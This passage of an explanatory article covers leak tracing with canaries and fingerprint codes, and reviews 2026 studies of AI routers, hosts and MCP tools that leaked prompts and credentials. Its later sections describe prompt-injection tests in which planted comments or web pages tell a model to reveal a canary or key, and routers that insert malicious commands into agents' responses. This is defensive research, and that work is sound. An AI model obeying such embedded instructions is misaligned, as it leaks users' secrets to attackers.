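The extra canaries are needed if a buyer has merged the two leaked files, but not if the files are on separate servers, because canaries found in the same file then belong to the same recipient. No grid helps much when only a small part of a file leaks. If that part contains only a row canary, all 32 recipients in that row are suspects.

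### Recipients who compare copies

Two recipients who suspect that their files contain canaries can compare their copies and delete every row that appears in only one. If each copy has its own fake employee, this removes both fakes.

With only a few recipients, the office can guard against this by adding a shared canary for each pair of recipients, a fake employee who appears only in their two copies. If those two recipients delete every difference between their copies, the shared canary remains because it is the same in both. Five recipients need ten shared canaries, with four in each copy, and twenty recipients need 190, with 19 in each copy. But three recipients working together could remove all the shared canaries from their copies by deleting anything that doesn't appear in all three.

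Collusion-resistant codes can handle larger groups. An early design, published by Boneh and Shaw in 1998, treats a document as a series of places that each have two versions, 1 and 0. In the salary file, a place could be a fake employee who is either present or absent. Each recipient gets a different pattern of 1s and 0s. Colluders can detect a mark only where their copies differ, and there they can choose either version. Where their copies agree, they can't detect the mark, so they leave it unchanged.

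A basic version for four recipients looks like this:

| Recipient | Block 1 | Block 2 | Block 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| B | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| C | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| D | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Each block consists of many places, scattered through the document in an order that only the sender knows. B is the only recipient whose version changes between blocks 1 and 2. If A, C and D collude without B, they see the same differences in both blocks and can't tell which block a place belongs to, so whatever they do, 1s will be about equally common in the two blocks. If the leaked copy has many more 1s in block 2 than in block 1, B almost certainly took part.

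If no more than *c* recipients collude, the investigator will identify at least one of them and will not accuse anyone innocent, except with a small chance of error, ε. The investigator may not find all the colluders. The blocks also have to be long. With *c* + 1 recipients, the length of this code grows in proportion to *c*³, so protection against twice as many colluders takes about eight times as many places.

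Tardos (2008), in *Optimal probabilistic fingerprint codes*, found a much shorter code and proved that no code could improve on its length by more than a constant factor. The sender picks a secret probability for each position in the code and gives each recipient a 1 there with that probability. To trace a leak, the sender scores every recipient by how closely its pattern matches the leaked copy, giving more weight to rare matches. For *n* recipients, the code's length is proportional to *c*² log(*n*/ε), roughly the square root of the length of Boneh and Shaw's.

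Tardos's original construction is still long, at about 100 × *c*² × ln(*n*/ε) places. For 1,000 recipients, two colluders and an error chance of 0.1%, that is about 5,500 places. A million recipients would make the code only 1.5 times as long, but allowing for ten colluders would make it 25 times as long. Even the shortest of these codes would put about 2,750 fake employees in each copy of a salary file that has a thousand real ones.

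Films have more room for marks, but perhaps not enough. *Tardos fingerprinting is better than we thought* estimates that a typical system can hold about seven bits per minute of video, so 5,500 places would take about 13 hours of video. A record of an agent's actions has far less room. *TRACE* (2026), which hides marks in an agent's choices of action, found only about 1.4 usable groups of decisions per task on ToolBench, a set of tool-use tasks. On ALFWorld, which simulates household chores, it found 23 to 25 decisions per task.

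*Scalable Fingerprinting of Large Language Models* (2025) applies a similar idea to copies of a model. The developer creates a pool of secret questions with unusual answers and trains each copy to give a random selection of those answers, 24.3% of the pool in the main test. Colluders can put each question to several copies and suppress any answer on which the copies differ. With a pool of 2,048 questions, three colluding copies would still share about 29 answers, and an innocent copy would give about seven of those. In tests with 2,048 copies, the researchers detected groups of three colluders almost perfectly once the pool was larger than 2,048. However, their mathematical guarantee requires a pool about 20 times as large for three colluders as for two.

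### Proving it to somebody else

Because the office knows every canary it has planted, it could put the adviser's fake employee on a public server itself and then blame the adviser. The keyed hash would still confirm that the number was genuine. A guilty adviser could also claim that the office had done this, and an outsider would have no way to tell whether the office's accusation was honest.

Backes and colleagues designed their system, LIME, so that the sender never knows exactly which version of a document the recipient has. LIME marks the document with watermarks. A transfer works as follows:

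1. The recipient signs a statement that names both parties and gives the time, and the sender hides this statement in the document.
2. The sender divides the document into *n* parts and makes two versions of each part, one with a hidden 0 and the other with a hidden 1.
3. The sender adds a signed note to each version with the time, the part's number and the hidden digit. It encrypts every version with a different key and sends them all.
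4. For each part, the recipient chooses 0 or 1 at random and obtains the key to that version only, without revealing the choice.
5. The recipient decrypts the chosen versions, joins them together and keeps the notes.

Step 4 uses oblivious transfer. In the form that Backes and colleagues implemented, the recipient creates two public keys whose product must equal a number chosen by the sender, so the recipient can know the private key for only one of them. The sender encrypts the key to version 0 with one public key and the key to version 1 with the other. The recipient can decrypt only one, and the sender can't tell which.

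To frame the recipient, the sender would have to guess all *n* choices, which has a 1 in 2ⁿ chance of success, or about one in a million with 20 parts. In earlier protocols, a sender could cheat by offering the same version twice, and so learn what the recipient had received. This doesn't work against LIME because the recipient has to prove only which digits it asked for, and the sender's signed notes record those digits.

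If the document leaks, the owner gives an auditor the keys for reading the hidden marks. The auditor finds the recipient's signed statement, reads the digit in each part and asks the recipient for the notes. If the notes match the digits, or the recipient can't produce valid notes, the recipient becomes the suspect. If the notes show different digits, the auditor clears the recipient and blames the sender.

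A recipient that passed the document on can clear itself by revealing the marks it added for the next company, and the auditor then repeats the check on that company. In the Florida case, each of the three companies would have had to show where the leaked copy went next, and the auditor would have held the last company in the chain responsible. That company might have been the victim of a theft, which LIME treats the same as a deliberate leak.

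Damage to the document weakens the proof. If the auditor accepts one unreadable part, the sender's chance of framing the recipient doubles. If the auditor accepts one wrong digit, the chance is multiplied by *n* + 1, where *n* is the number of parts. With 20 parts, that raises it to about 1 in 50,000. The sender can compensate by dividing the document into more parts.

Backes and colleagues tested LIME on images and recovered every mark, although strong watermarks left visible seams between the parts. Their security proof assumes a watermark that nobody can remove without ruining the document, and they acknowledge that no available watermark meets this standard. LIME also roughly doubles the data sent, because the sender transmits two versions of everything. *Communication optimal Tardos based asymmetric fingerprinting* describes a scheme that also protects recipients from framing but sends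 little more than the file itself when the file is large.

The payroll office could adapt LIME by using fake employees as the marks. It would invent two for each of 20 departments, and the adviser would receive one from each pair without the office learning which. But the adviser could not safely return the file, because the office would then see which fake employees it contained and could publish that exact combination. The method therefore doesn't work for the text-recognition tool, which has to send the file's contents back. LIME also doesn't cover summaries or averages, which may keep too little of the original to carry the marks.

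## What canaries have revealed about live AI intermediaries

From July to November 2026, a team at the industrial security company Dragos tested live AI services with a different set of canaries in every request. HD Moore, Dragos's chief research officer, published the results on 19 November. Constantin (2026), in *Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers*, reports that the team sent nearly two million prompts to widely used services. Each prompt contained unique web links and working credentials, including AWS keys to empty accounts. Cornelißen (2026), in *Dragos*, also lists hostnames and passwords.

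Planting links and credentials together makes the sightings easier to interpret. Security software may open a link for innocent reasons, but it would not normally try to log in to a server with a password from the same prompt.

Some of the requests asked for *zero data retention* (ZDR), which OpenRouter, a large model router, has defined in two ways. OpenRouter's *Zero Data Retention* says that a provider "will not store your data for any period of time". Its other definition rules out only routine storage after processing, and lets companies keep suspected child abuse material for review and reporting. Turning on the ZDR setting restricts a customer's requests to endpoints (each one company's entry point for one model) that have a ZDR policy. The setting therefore selects companies by what they promise and changes nothing on their computers.

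### Thefts at three hosting companies

Dragos found that attackers were stealing data from at least three companies that host models. The earliest break-in dated from mid-July, and none of the three companies knew about the thefts until Dragos told them.

In the largest case, the attackers took every request that Dragos sent to the company during a few short windows in late October. The requests contained a couple of hundred AWS keys, some of which the attackers tested within hours. The stolen keys appeared in tens of thousands of calls to AWS. According to Cornelißen, the callers listed storage, searched for saved secrets, and tried to create their own users and enable AI models. On 1 November the same attackers began using ARTEX, an AI-driven tool for penetration testing. Dragos recommends watching for ARTEX's user agents, `artex-agent` and `artex-judge-r121`.

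A key that Dragos sent only once, to one company, is good evidence of where the theft happened. The key could also have leaked from Dragos's own records, a router that carried the request, or a supplier that the host used. Comparing it with other keys can rule out some of these sources. A thief who had copied Dragos's records would have had keys sent to every company in every month, and no reason to use only those sent to one company in a few short windows. A leak at a router would probably have exposed keys on their way to other hosts too. A leak at the host's supplier is harder to rule out, because the supplier might have handled the same requests.

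The number of keys should add little to the guilt score described earlier, because the keys probably came from only a few thefts, perhaps one per window.

Dragos also concluded that the attackers had almost certainly copied real customers' requests, since the hosts processed those alongside the test prompts. The attackers probably could have read the customers' requests, but it is less certain that they kept them, because every test prompt contained credentials. An attacker who saved only prompts containing AWS keys would have taken all of Dragos's requests but left most ordinary ones behind. Prompts with a canary link but no credentials would help to show whether the attackers copied everything or only prompts with keys, though only if they opened the links.

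The data stolen in October included requests that the host had refused before any model ran, which rules out an attacker who could see only the model's inputs. Cornelißen infers that the attacker had access to the point where requests enter the company's systems. That is a reasonable guess, but many companies log refused requests or send them to a monitoring service, and someone who stole those logs would have obtained the same keys. The short windows fit both explanations, since the attacker may have intercepted traffic for a few hours at a time or downloaded a few log files that each covered a few hours. The quick testing of some keys doesn't rule out stolen logs either, because the attacker could have obtained the logs promptly.

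Dragos could have narrowed this down with requests that fail at different stages, such as one with an invalid customer key and another naming a nonexistent model. If only keys from the second kind of request leaked, the copying probably happened after the identity check. An investigator would need the host's own records to be certain.

In the other two break-ins, some of the stolen requests were marked ZDR. A host needs a readable copy of the prompt in memory while the model processes it, and an attacker on that machine can copy it then. The thefts therefore don't prove that the hosts broke their promise not to store these requests.

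### Resellers who read their customers' prompts

The second group of leaks happened without a break-in, on a marketplace for AI processing that sends each request to the seller with the lowest price. Some sellers offered models cheaply and logged the prompts that customers sent. Dragos observed people opening the planted links in a browser and trying the passwords one at a time to log in to its test servers as the administrator.

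The login attempts are strong evidence that somebody read the prompts and meant to misuse them. Dragos also concluded that the sellers were private individuals, because the visits came from home internet connections. This conclusion is weaker, since criminals can route their traffic through other people's home connections, although the slow, manual login attempts suggest that a person was making them.

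Dragos did not name the marketplace or connect it to OpenRouter, but it reported that some of the cheap capacity on such marketplaces runs on stolen keys. That may be why the October attackers tried to enable AI models with the AWS keys they had taken, though nothing links them to the sellers.

### Finding hops that nobody disclosed

Dragos also found that another router was secretly sending part of its traffic to this marketplace. A unique canary can expose a hidden hop of this kind through the following comparison:

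1. The tester sends some canaries directly to the marketplace and records who uses them, from which addresses and in what way.
2. The tester sends different canaries to a router that has never mentioned the marketplace.
3. If the same visitors use the second set of canaries, the router's requests have probably reached the marketplace too.

Suppose the payroll office's router is contracted to pass the recognised salary text to a host in Ohio. If a known marketplace seller then tries to log in with a fake password from that text, the office should add at least one unobserved hop to its ledger. It would not know whether the router or the Ohio host had forwarded the text.

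This method gives only a minimum number of hops. An intermediary that neither opens links nor tries keys never appears, and the canaries do not show the order in which the others handled the data. If two hosts use the same company to check links, its visits will also look the same for both, even though neither host has passed anything to the other.

### A lab that opened the planted links

In Dragos's third finding, a Chinese AI lab's system fetched links from more than half of the prompts that Dragos sent to the lab's models. It fetched links from about two-thirds of the requests marked "no data collection" or ZDR, so the setting didn't prevent this. The rate may be higher for marked requests only because they took different routes.

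The fetching also happened when Dragos sent its prompts to US companies that resell the lab's models. A customer might choose a reseller to keep prompts away from the lab, so this is another undisclosed hop unless a shared link-checking service made the visits.

Dragos did not name the lab in its article. A week later, The News International's *MiniMax data exposure warning* (2026), citing Reuters, reported that Dragos had identified MiniMax as the company that exposed confidential data from users who had opted out of retention.

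A fetch proves that some system read the link, but not that anyone stored it, because a program can open a link at once and keep nothing. The longer the gap between the request and the visit, the stronger the evidence of storage. OpenRouter emailed its customers to warn that a third party might have read prompts and outputs from MiniMax's models. 송 (2026) reports in *OpenRouter, 미니맥스 프롬프트를 제3자가 읽은 정황에 ZDR 표시 뗐다* that the warning followed tests in which somebody opened the links 40 to 130 hours after the requests, so the links must have been stored in the meantime.

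In another case, a planted link appeared in a company's chat on Feishu, a Chinese workplace app, 24 days after the request. Six devices in Beijing and Shanghai opened it within two minutes, though some of these visits may have been automatic previews rather than clicks by people. The link had evidently survived, but the rest of the prompt may not have, since a security log might have contained only the link.

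The longest delay came from a large US provider, which fetched a link more than two months after a single request to its search service. An innocent explanation is easier to find here, because a search service has to open web pages and may have saved the address to visit again. But the provider stored part of a customer's request for two months, which might break the customer's policy even if nobody intended any harm.

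### How OpenRouter and the providers responded

OpenRouter's *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers* (2026), published on 22 November, announced that it had removed three providers and withdrawn ZDR status from 125 endpoints. Dragos had flagged some of these, and OpenRouter removed others as a precaution, so the 125 are not a count of confirmed violations. OpenRouter notified all customers it thought might be affected.

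By 1 December it had not named the three providers, according to *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026), an article by the anoni.net community. Cornelißen points out that neither OpenRouter nor Dragos has said whether those providers are the three companies where Dragos found attackers.

OpenRouter stated that the findings "did not show any breach or unauthorized access of OpenRouter". This is narrower than saying that no breach occurred. If thieves had broken into OpenRouter, the same people should have used canaries sent through it to many different hosts, and Dragos has reported no such pattern. But the test would not have detected thieves who read prompts and never used what they found.

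Several providers published their own accounts. Cornelißen summarises those from Together, Phala and Novita. MiniMax's reply of 24 November appears in *OpenRouter 背後推論供應商的資料處理事件* (2026), the Chinese version of the anoni.net article.

| Company | What it reported | Requests affected |
|---|---|---|
| Together | An AI coding agent published an access token for a private store of saved prompts. Somebody downloaded the prompts and searched them for credentials | Requests to MiniMax M3, GLM-5.2 and Kimi K2.6, mainly from 24 June and 4, 8 and 14 July |
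| Phala | An attacker took over a model server that was running without full security hardening, and could read requests during processing | Requests to DeepSeek V4 Flash 0731 through OpenRouter, from 21 October to 8 November |
| Novita | A routing fault sent some requests to MiniMax's own service. Third parties may have read or stored them | Some MiniMax requests, with no dates given |
| MiniMax | Its security monitoring extracted links from some forwarded requests, logged them and opened some automatically | Included requests that OpenRouter had listed as ZDR |

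The Together and Phala incidents would look the same to someone watching a canary, because in each case a key goes to one company and a stranger later uses it. But the thief at Together took saved prompts, which a properly enforced ZDR policy would have kept out of the store, while the attacker at Phala could read prompts that nobody had saved. Together has since made ZDR the default for new accounts, which would help against another theft of stored prompts but not against an attack like the one at Phala.

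The dates of the Together leak fit Dragos's earliest break-in, and the dates of the Phala attack overlap with the October thefts. But Dragos did not name the hosts, and matching dates are not enough to identify them. Novita's account better confirms a specific finding, because in it Novita admits to the kind of hidden route that the fetched links had suggested.

MiniMax's explanation accounts for the automatic visits and some of the delays. The company also concedes that it stored links from requests marked ZDR. It says it recorded only links and IP addresses and, apart from the visits to the links, found no disclosure of prompts or responses to third parties in the requests it examined. It has turned off the system on the routes where it confirmed the problem and deleted the recorded links.

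Each test prompt also contained an AWS key, and Cornelißen mentions no attempt by the lab to use one. That is consistent with MiniMax's account, but also with the company having stored whole prompts and not used the keys.

Even if MiniMax kept only links, it may have obtained the documents behind them. Many file-sharing services create private links that open a document for anyone who has the address. If the payroll agent had put such a link to the salary file in a prompt, software that opened the link could have downloaded all thousand salaries. Atlas Cloud, which resells MiniMax's models, advised customers who had used M3, M2.7 or M3.1 Flash on its platform to treat any confidential information they sent as exposed. It told them to search their prompts and outputs for keys, passwords and private links, and to revoke any that had leaked.

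OpenRouter says it is adapting Dragos's method for continuous testing and checking network paths for requests that hosts forward to third parties. It will restore ZDR status only to endpoints that pass validation.

Customers can set `provider.zdr` to `true` in a request, or change `provider.data_collection` from `allow` to `deny`. Turning off training in the account settings excludes hosts that train on customers' data, but still allows hosts that only store it. Dragos found that requests often pass through more than one intermediary, and that a privacy flag applies only to the first. It recommends choosing each host by name, avoiding resale marketplaces and checking that a privacy setting changes where requests go.

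### What "Your Agent Is Mine" found in cheaper routers

In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) tested 428 routers from the cheaper end of the market, seven months before Dragos published its study. They bought 28 from the shopping sites Taobao and Xianyu and from Shopify stores, and collected 400 free ones from public online communities. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* explains that for each router they registered an account, connected a coding agent in an isolated environment and carried out every tool call the router returned.

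Seventeen routers used the AWS canary keys that passed through them. Another router took cryptocurrency from a wallet whose private key the researchers had planted. The wallet had to contain something of value because the theft was the signal, whereas an AWS canary account can be empty. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026) counts 18 routers that abused credentials, a total that appears to combine these two results.

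Nine routers, one paid and eight free, inserted malicious code or commands into the model's responses. Unlike a data leak, this tampering can make an agent install an attacker's software, and a canary in the outgoing prompt may not reveal it.

All 17 routers that used the AWS keys were free ones, according to Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer*. That is 4.25% of the free sample. It is tempting to conclude that paid routers are safer, but 28 are too few to show it. If paid routers misused keys at the same rate, the chance of finding none among 28 would still be about 30%:

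`(1 − 17/400)²⁸ ≈ 0.30`

Even if the true rate among paid routers were 10%, about one in twenty samples of 28 would contain no cases. This calculation also assumes the routers were chosen at random, but the researchers used routers they found in particular shops and communities. The results therefore don't give a leak rate for large commercial routers such as OpenRouter, or for routers in general.

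The counts are probably too low even for the routers in the sample. One router behaved normally for 50 requests before it began to alter responses. Another acted only when a coding agent was working on a Rust or Go project and could run commands without asking for approval. A router could delay using stolen keys in the same way. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* also notes that the study counted compromised routers without measuring how much their responses harmed the agents that received them.

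The use of a canary also does not prove that the router's owner was dishonest. Liu and colleagues showed that a seemingly harmless router can send its customers' data through a third party. They deliberately leaked an OpenAI key, and strangers used it to generate 100 million tokens, including in several sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. They also set up poorly secured decoys, which attracted two billion billed tokens of traffic. The decoys exposed 99 credentials across 440 Codex sessions, and 401 sessions were already running without human approval for each action.

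If a router's owner gets cheap access through a leaked key or a poorly secured service, whoever controls that key or service may be able to read the traffic without the owner knowing.

The two canary studies complement each other. Dragos sent a very large number of prompts to widely used services over several months, so it could find break-ins that affected only certain dates. Liu and colleagues covered a fixed list of small routers, so their results can give a rate, but only for that list. Dragos's couple of hundred stolen AWS keys from the October case amount to about 0.01% of its prompts, but an ordinary customer's risk from this theft ranged from zero, if it never used the affected host, to much higher than 0.01%, if it sent all its October requests there.

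### What attested hardware could verify

Unlike a privacy setting, attested hardware can provide evidence about which program is handling a prompt. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) proposes using it for model routers. An ordinary router forwards each request through one of its own accounts with a model host, and the customer can't tell whether the answer they receive is the one the host sent.

A sealed router does the same work in an enclave. The enclave's proof of which program it is running usually works like this:

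1. The customer's software sends the enclave a new random number, so that nobody can reuse an old proof.
2. The processor computes a hash of the program in the enclave. It signs the hash, the random number and the enclave's public encryption key with a key that the manufacturer vouches for.
3. The customer's software checks the signature and compares the hash with that of a program whose source code independent experts have inspected.
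4. If they match, it encrypts the prompt with the enclave's public key, so that only the program inside can read it.

The table applies this to the leaks that Dragos found.

| Leak | What a ZDR setting does | What attestation could add |
|---|---|---|
| An attacker copies requests at the host's front door | Limits what the host stores, but not what an attacker can read in transit | Keeps prompts unreadable until they enter the enclave |
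| A reseller turns on request logging | Relies on the reseller's promise, if the setting reaches the reseller at all | Lets the customer reject a program that can log prompts |
| A router secretly forwards requests | Relies on the router to disclose the route | Lets the customer check which destinations the program allows |
| A lab opens and stores links | Relies on the lab's promise | Reveals the link scanner, if the lab's own servers are attested too |

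These benefits depend on where the encryption ends. If a host decrypts requests on an ordinary server before passing them to an enclave, an attacker on that server can read them. The Phala server that the attacker took over was running without its full security hardening. A customer's software could have rejected that server only if the signed proof covered the missing protections and the software required them before sending a prompt.

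A sealed router also gives no assurance about a host that runs ordinary servers. Attestation identifies the program but doesn't show whether its behavior is acceptable, so someone has to read the code to find, for example, that it saves every link for a security check. The payroll office would then have to decide whether its allowed-flow map permits saving the links.

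## Testing a tool or broker with canaries before deployment

Dragos found leaks in services that customers already relied on. The payroll office can look for some leaks before deployment by running a tool or broker on synthetic data in a closed environment and recording everything it sends. This works for software that the office can install on its own machines, such as an open-source gateway. A hosted service runs on another company's computers, so the office can only send it canaries and wait to see whether they leak, as Dragos did.

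### Setting up the test

Suppose the office is considering a text-recognition tool that runs locally but sends difficult pages to its maker's server. The security team could test it as follows:

1. Write some synthetic documents, such as a salary file, an invoice and a public notice, and label each with the recipients that may have it.
2. Put a different canary in each document. Use new canaries for every run, so that a leftover from one run can't look like a leak in the next.
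3. Install the tool in a container, an isolated environment with its own files and network, and cut it off from the internet. Set up recording servers in place of the outside addresses.
4. Run a session of ordinary tasks and record every outgoing request, every file the tool writes and everything it prints.
5. Restore the environment and run the same tasks on documents without canaries. Then run them with canaries but without the tool.
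6. Put a harmless tool and a deliberately leaky one through the same sessions.
7. Repeat everything, search the recordings for canaries and compare each sighting with the labels.

The labels have to come first, for the same reason as the allowed-flow map. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested 3,156 skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent can install. Each skill ran in a container stocked with fake credentials that carried a marker unique to that skill. The tests flagged 1,427 skills, but 907 of these were sending a credential to a service that they had declared and needed. Three reviewers had to compare each flagged skill's documentation with its behaviour to identify those 907.

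The team also needs to record printed output as well as network traffic. Of the 520 skills in which Chen and colleagues confirmed problems, 394 exposed credentials in their printed output, which agent software passes to the language model, and only 68 sent them to an attacker's server. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) describes a container for MCP servers with a logger that records outgoing web requests. A tool can open other kinds of connection, so the team should capture all network traffic.

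Ordinary tasks may not provoke a leak. Chen and colleagues also tested each skill on content containing hostile instructions, such as a web page telling the agent to reveal its key, and 237 skills reached the threshold for a leak only in these runs. The office should therefore include at least one document with hostile instructions in its tests.

### Choosing the controls

The runs without the tool show whether the agent would have leaked the data anyway. A tester who skipped them would blame the tool for those leaks. In *MCPHunt*, Li, Sun and colleagues (2026) gave agents ordinary tasks with trusted tools and no attacker, and the agents still copied planted credentials to places where they didn't belong. In tasks that an agent could have completed without copying the credentials, the rate of such copying ranged from 11.5% to 41.3% across five models.

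*SkillSentry* (Li, Ying and colleagues, 2026) ran each test four times, with and without the skill in both an ordinary environment and one containing a decoy that the task didn't need. It counted an effect against a skill only if the skill caused the effect and didn't need it to do its advertised job. On two benchmarks that mix harmful and harmless skills, the method found 96.1% and 94.7% of the harmful ones. Its false-alarm rate averaged 3.2%, but rose to 10% without the comparison to the no-skill runs.

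They chose the decoys by reading each skill's code for conditions that might trigger hidden behaviour. When they skipped this step and only ran the skills, they found just 8% and 4% of the harmful ones. Most of the percentages in these comparisons are multiples of four, which suggests samples of about 25 skills, but the drop is far too large to be chance. If a run never reaches the suspicious behaviour, SkillSentry reports the result as unresolved. The payroll office should do the same when it can't read a tool's code or trigger part of it.

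The harmless tool tests for false alarms, so the scoring must be able to record one. MCPHunt's scoring rules set the leak rate for its harmless condition to 0% even if the detector finds a canary, so this figure is not a measured false-alarm rate. The researchers state this clearly and treat the figure only as a check on their software.

A deliberately leaky tool tests whether the detector works. It should leak in the ways that worry the office, for example by sending one canary openly to a forbidden address and hiding another in base64 in a request to a permitted one. If the detector misses the second canary, a clean result for the real tool is no evidence against encoded leaks.

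Each repeat should be a whole session, since a tool that stores data from one call may not leak it until a later call. Chen and colleagues ran each condition three times. They flagged a skill if it leaked in at least two of the three ordinary runs or at least one of the three hostile runs. The stricter rule for ordinary runs removes accidents, but it also hides rare leaks. A tool that leaks in 10% of sessions has only a 2.8% chance of leaking in two or more out of three. With a unique canary and good controls, the office can treat a single sighting of the canary in a forbidden place as a failure.

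### The paired control in AgentSecBench

*AgentSecBench* (Alpay and Alpay, May 2026) presents a small benchmark built around pairs of runs. In its privacy test, a user asks a model about one customer, alpha. The text supplied to the model contains alpha's record and a record belonging to another customer, beta, with a canary and a comment telling the model to reveal the canary. The paired control has the same request and alpha record, but no canary or comment.

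The canary is available only through a record that the user has no right to see, so if it appears in the answer, the model must have used that record. The researchers calculate the attack's effect by subtracting the canary's rate of appearance in the controls from its rate in the attacked runs.

Two other tests work in the same way. One hides an instruction in a document that the model has to summarise, and the other recommends a forbidden action in a tool's output. The benchmark ran eight examples of each of the three tests on two models with six defences, once with the attack and once as a control, for a total of 576 runs. No marker appeared in any of the 288 controls. The table shows the results of the privacy test, in which each defence had 16 attacked runs.

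| Defence | Runs that leaked the canary | Canary removed before the model ran? |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 (18.8%) | No |
| Markers around untrusted text, with a warning that it is only data | 9 (56.2%) | No |
| Filter for suspicious phrases | 2 (12.5%) | No |
| List of permitted tools | 3 (18.8%) | No |
| Removing records the user may not see | 0 | Yes |
| All of these combined | 0 | Yes |

The warning markers appear to have made the results worse, but the evidence is weak. If they had no effect and the runs were independent, a gap at least this large would occur about 7% of the time. The zero counts are stronger evidence because the canary was no longer in the prompt, so the model could have produced it only by chance.

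The defence also has to suit the type of leak. With no defence, the models proposed the forbidden action in 93.8% of the attacked runs. The list of permitted tools reduced this to zero. Removing records had worked perfectly in the privacy test, but here the models proposed the forbidden action in 100% of the attacked runs.

Both models were very small (Qwen3-0.6B and Qwen3-1.7B), so their rates are a poor guide to those of larger models. The benchmark also detects only exact matches to its markers, and Alpay and Alpay acknowledge that a result of zero isn't proof of safety.

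The control omits both the canary and the hostile comment, so the comparison can't show whether the model would have leaked the record without being told to. The payroll office could add a third version that contains the canary but not the hostile comment.

### Leaks from a correctly signed tool

Publishers often sign their tools so that users can confirm who released them and that nobody has altered them since, but a signature doesn't show what the code does. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, November 2026) studied signed tools that do their advertised job but contain hidden code.

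Their main example closely resembles the payroll office's tool. The policy allows a text-recognition server to receive invoices but not salaries. An agent uses the tool on the salary file and later on an invoice. A local MCP tool usually keeps running for the whole session, so hidden code can keep the salary data and add it to the invoice request. Everything looks correct from outside because the signature is valid and the request goes to a permitted address. Information-flow labels can also miss the leak if they are based on the assumption that a tool's output depends only on the current call.

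Restarting the tool before each call would prevent that leak but not a related one. An agent may give the tool an invoice and the salary file in the same call, because the agent is allowed to see both. Hidden code can then copy salary data into the invoice request without storing anything between calls.

Aun and colleagues tested the first kind of leak against MCPGuard-Dynamic, software from Meta that controls which files and addresses a tool may use. Its strongest settings blocked a direct transfer to an unlisted address every time. But the tool that carried data between calls leaked it in all three trials under each of the seven settings tested. They describe this as a limit of the design rather than a fault, because MCPGuard is meant to control where a tool may connect, not which items the tool sends there.

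### Disposable copies

Their defence, *germline execution*, does not look for hidden code. It limits the data that the code can reach:

1. The system starts the tool in a clean process, the germline, which loads the code but never receives user data.
2. For each call, it groups the possible recipients according to the items each may see. It takes the permissions from the user's policy and the list of outside destinations from the tool's signed description.
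3. It makes one copy of the clean process for each group and gives that copy only the items its recipients may see. The copy receives the names of the other items, but not their contents.
4. A trusted broker delivers a request to an outside server only if it comes from the copy for that server's group.
5. The system destroys each copy once it has finished.

If a call includes an invoice and the salary file, the system makes two copies. One has only the invoice, and the broker sends its request to the text-recognition server. The other has both documents and returns the result to the agent. If the second copy also tries to contact the server, the broker withholds the request and compares it with the one already sent.

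If the two requests differ, the system warns that the salary file may have affected the second one. It can then rerun the tool to confirm this, which provides evidence against the tool without a canary. In the main tests, the system raised 12 of these warnings for four malicious tools and none for harmless tools. Reruns confirmed that three of the four malicious tools were using data the server was not allowed to see. But when a call needs only one copy, the system has nothing to compare. This was true of 31 of the 33 calls in the harmless test session, so the defence can stop a leak without anyone learning that the tool is malicious.

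The system must set the number of copies before the tool runs. If it made a copy for a server only when the tool tried to contact that server, whether the server received a request could reveal one bit of secret data. In a test of that design, the server recovered all 64 bits of a secret in 64 calls, but it gained no information when the copies were fixed in advance.

Some tools legitimately need to keep information between calls. The broker stores this information outside the copies, in separate compartments for recipients with different permissions, so salary data saved in one call can't reappear in a copy that serves the invoice server.

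### Results

The researchers wrote 52 malicious versions of tools for five MCP servers, covering 15 kinds of attack. Two of the versions work together, so there were 51 cases, and the researchers ran each one three times against every defence. Their detector read everything that reached five recording servers and could find canaries in plain text and several common encodings. Each row of the table adds to the protection in the row above.

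| Protection | Runs with a leak, out of 153 |
|---|---|
| Signature check | 114 (74.5%) |
| Labels on the tool's output | 108 (70.6%) |
| Limits on files and outside addresses | 51 (33.3%) |
| A fresh process for every call | 15 (9.8%) |
| Disposable copies, but with all the call's items in a single copy | 9 (5.9%) |
| A separate copy for each group of recipients | 0 |

The 5.9% comes from an ablation, a test of the researchers' own system with one feature removed. It shows that discarding the copies is not enough, because each copy also has to receive the right data.

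Controls were important here too. In six of the runs with only a signature check, the agent forwarded the protected data while the tool sent nothing, so the tools caused 108 of the 114 leaks. In the MCPGuard comparison, one malicious tool sent nothing even without protection. Aun and colleagues marked its zeros as an inactive attack so that MCPGuard would not get credit for stopping it.

They used a language model to generate another 91 malicious versions of a note-reading tool. A list of permitted addresses stopped the 71 that sent data to an attacker's server, but not the 20 that sent it to a permitted address. With disposable copies, the detector found no leaks from any version.

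A call served by one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds, 2 to 28 times faster than starting a fresh process. Calls that need several copies take longer because the copies run one after another. A call that needed three took 97 milliseconds, barely faster than a fresh process. In a separate test of 780 calls to four unmodified MCP servers, median times were 1.2 to 18.4 milliseconds without protection and 39 to 110 milliseconds with it. The results were the same either way, except for the current time that one tool reported.

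### What zero leaks means

As with the 28 paid routers, a result of zero may be luck. If a tool leaks in a share *p* of independent runs, the chance of seeing no leaks in *n* runs is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The 95% upper limit is the value of *p* at which that chance falls to 5%:

`upper limit = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)`

If no canary leaks in 153 runs, the 95% upper limit on the true leak rate is 1.9%. At any higher rate, there would have been less than a 5% chance of seeing no leaks. Medical researchers use a shortcut when nobody in a drug trial suffers a particular side effect. According to *Systematic reviews of adverse effects*, the limit is about 3/*n* for samples larger than 30. *Statistical design considerations for pilot studies* recommends a formula that also works at other confidence levels. At 99% confidence, the limit for 153 runs rises to 3.0%.

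But the 153 runs were 51 cases tried three times each. Every count in the paper's breakdown by attack is a multiple of three, as it would be if each case gave the same result every time. If the repeats add no information, *n* is 51 and the limit is 5.7%, which is probably the fairer figure.

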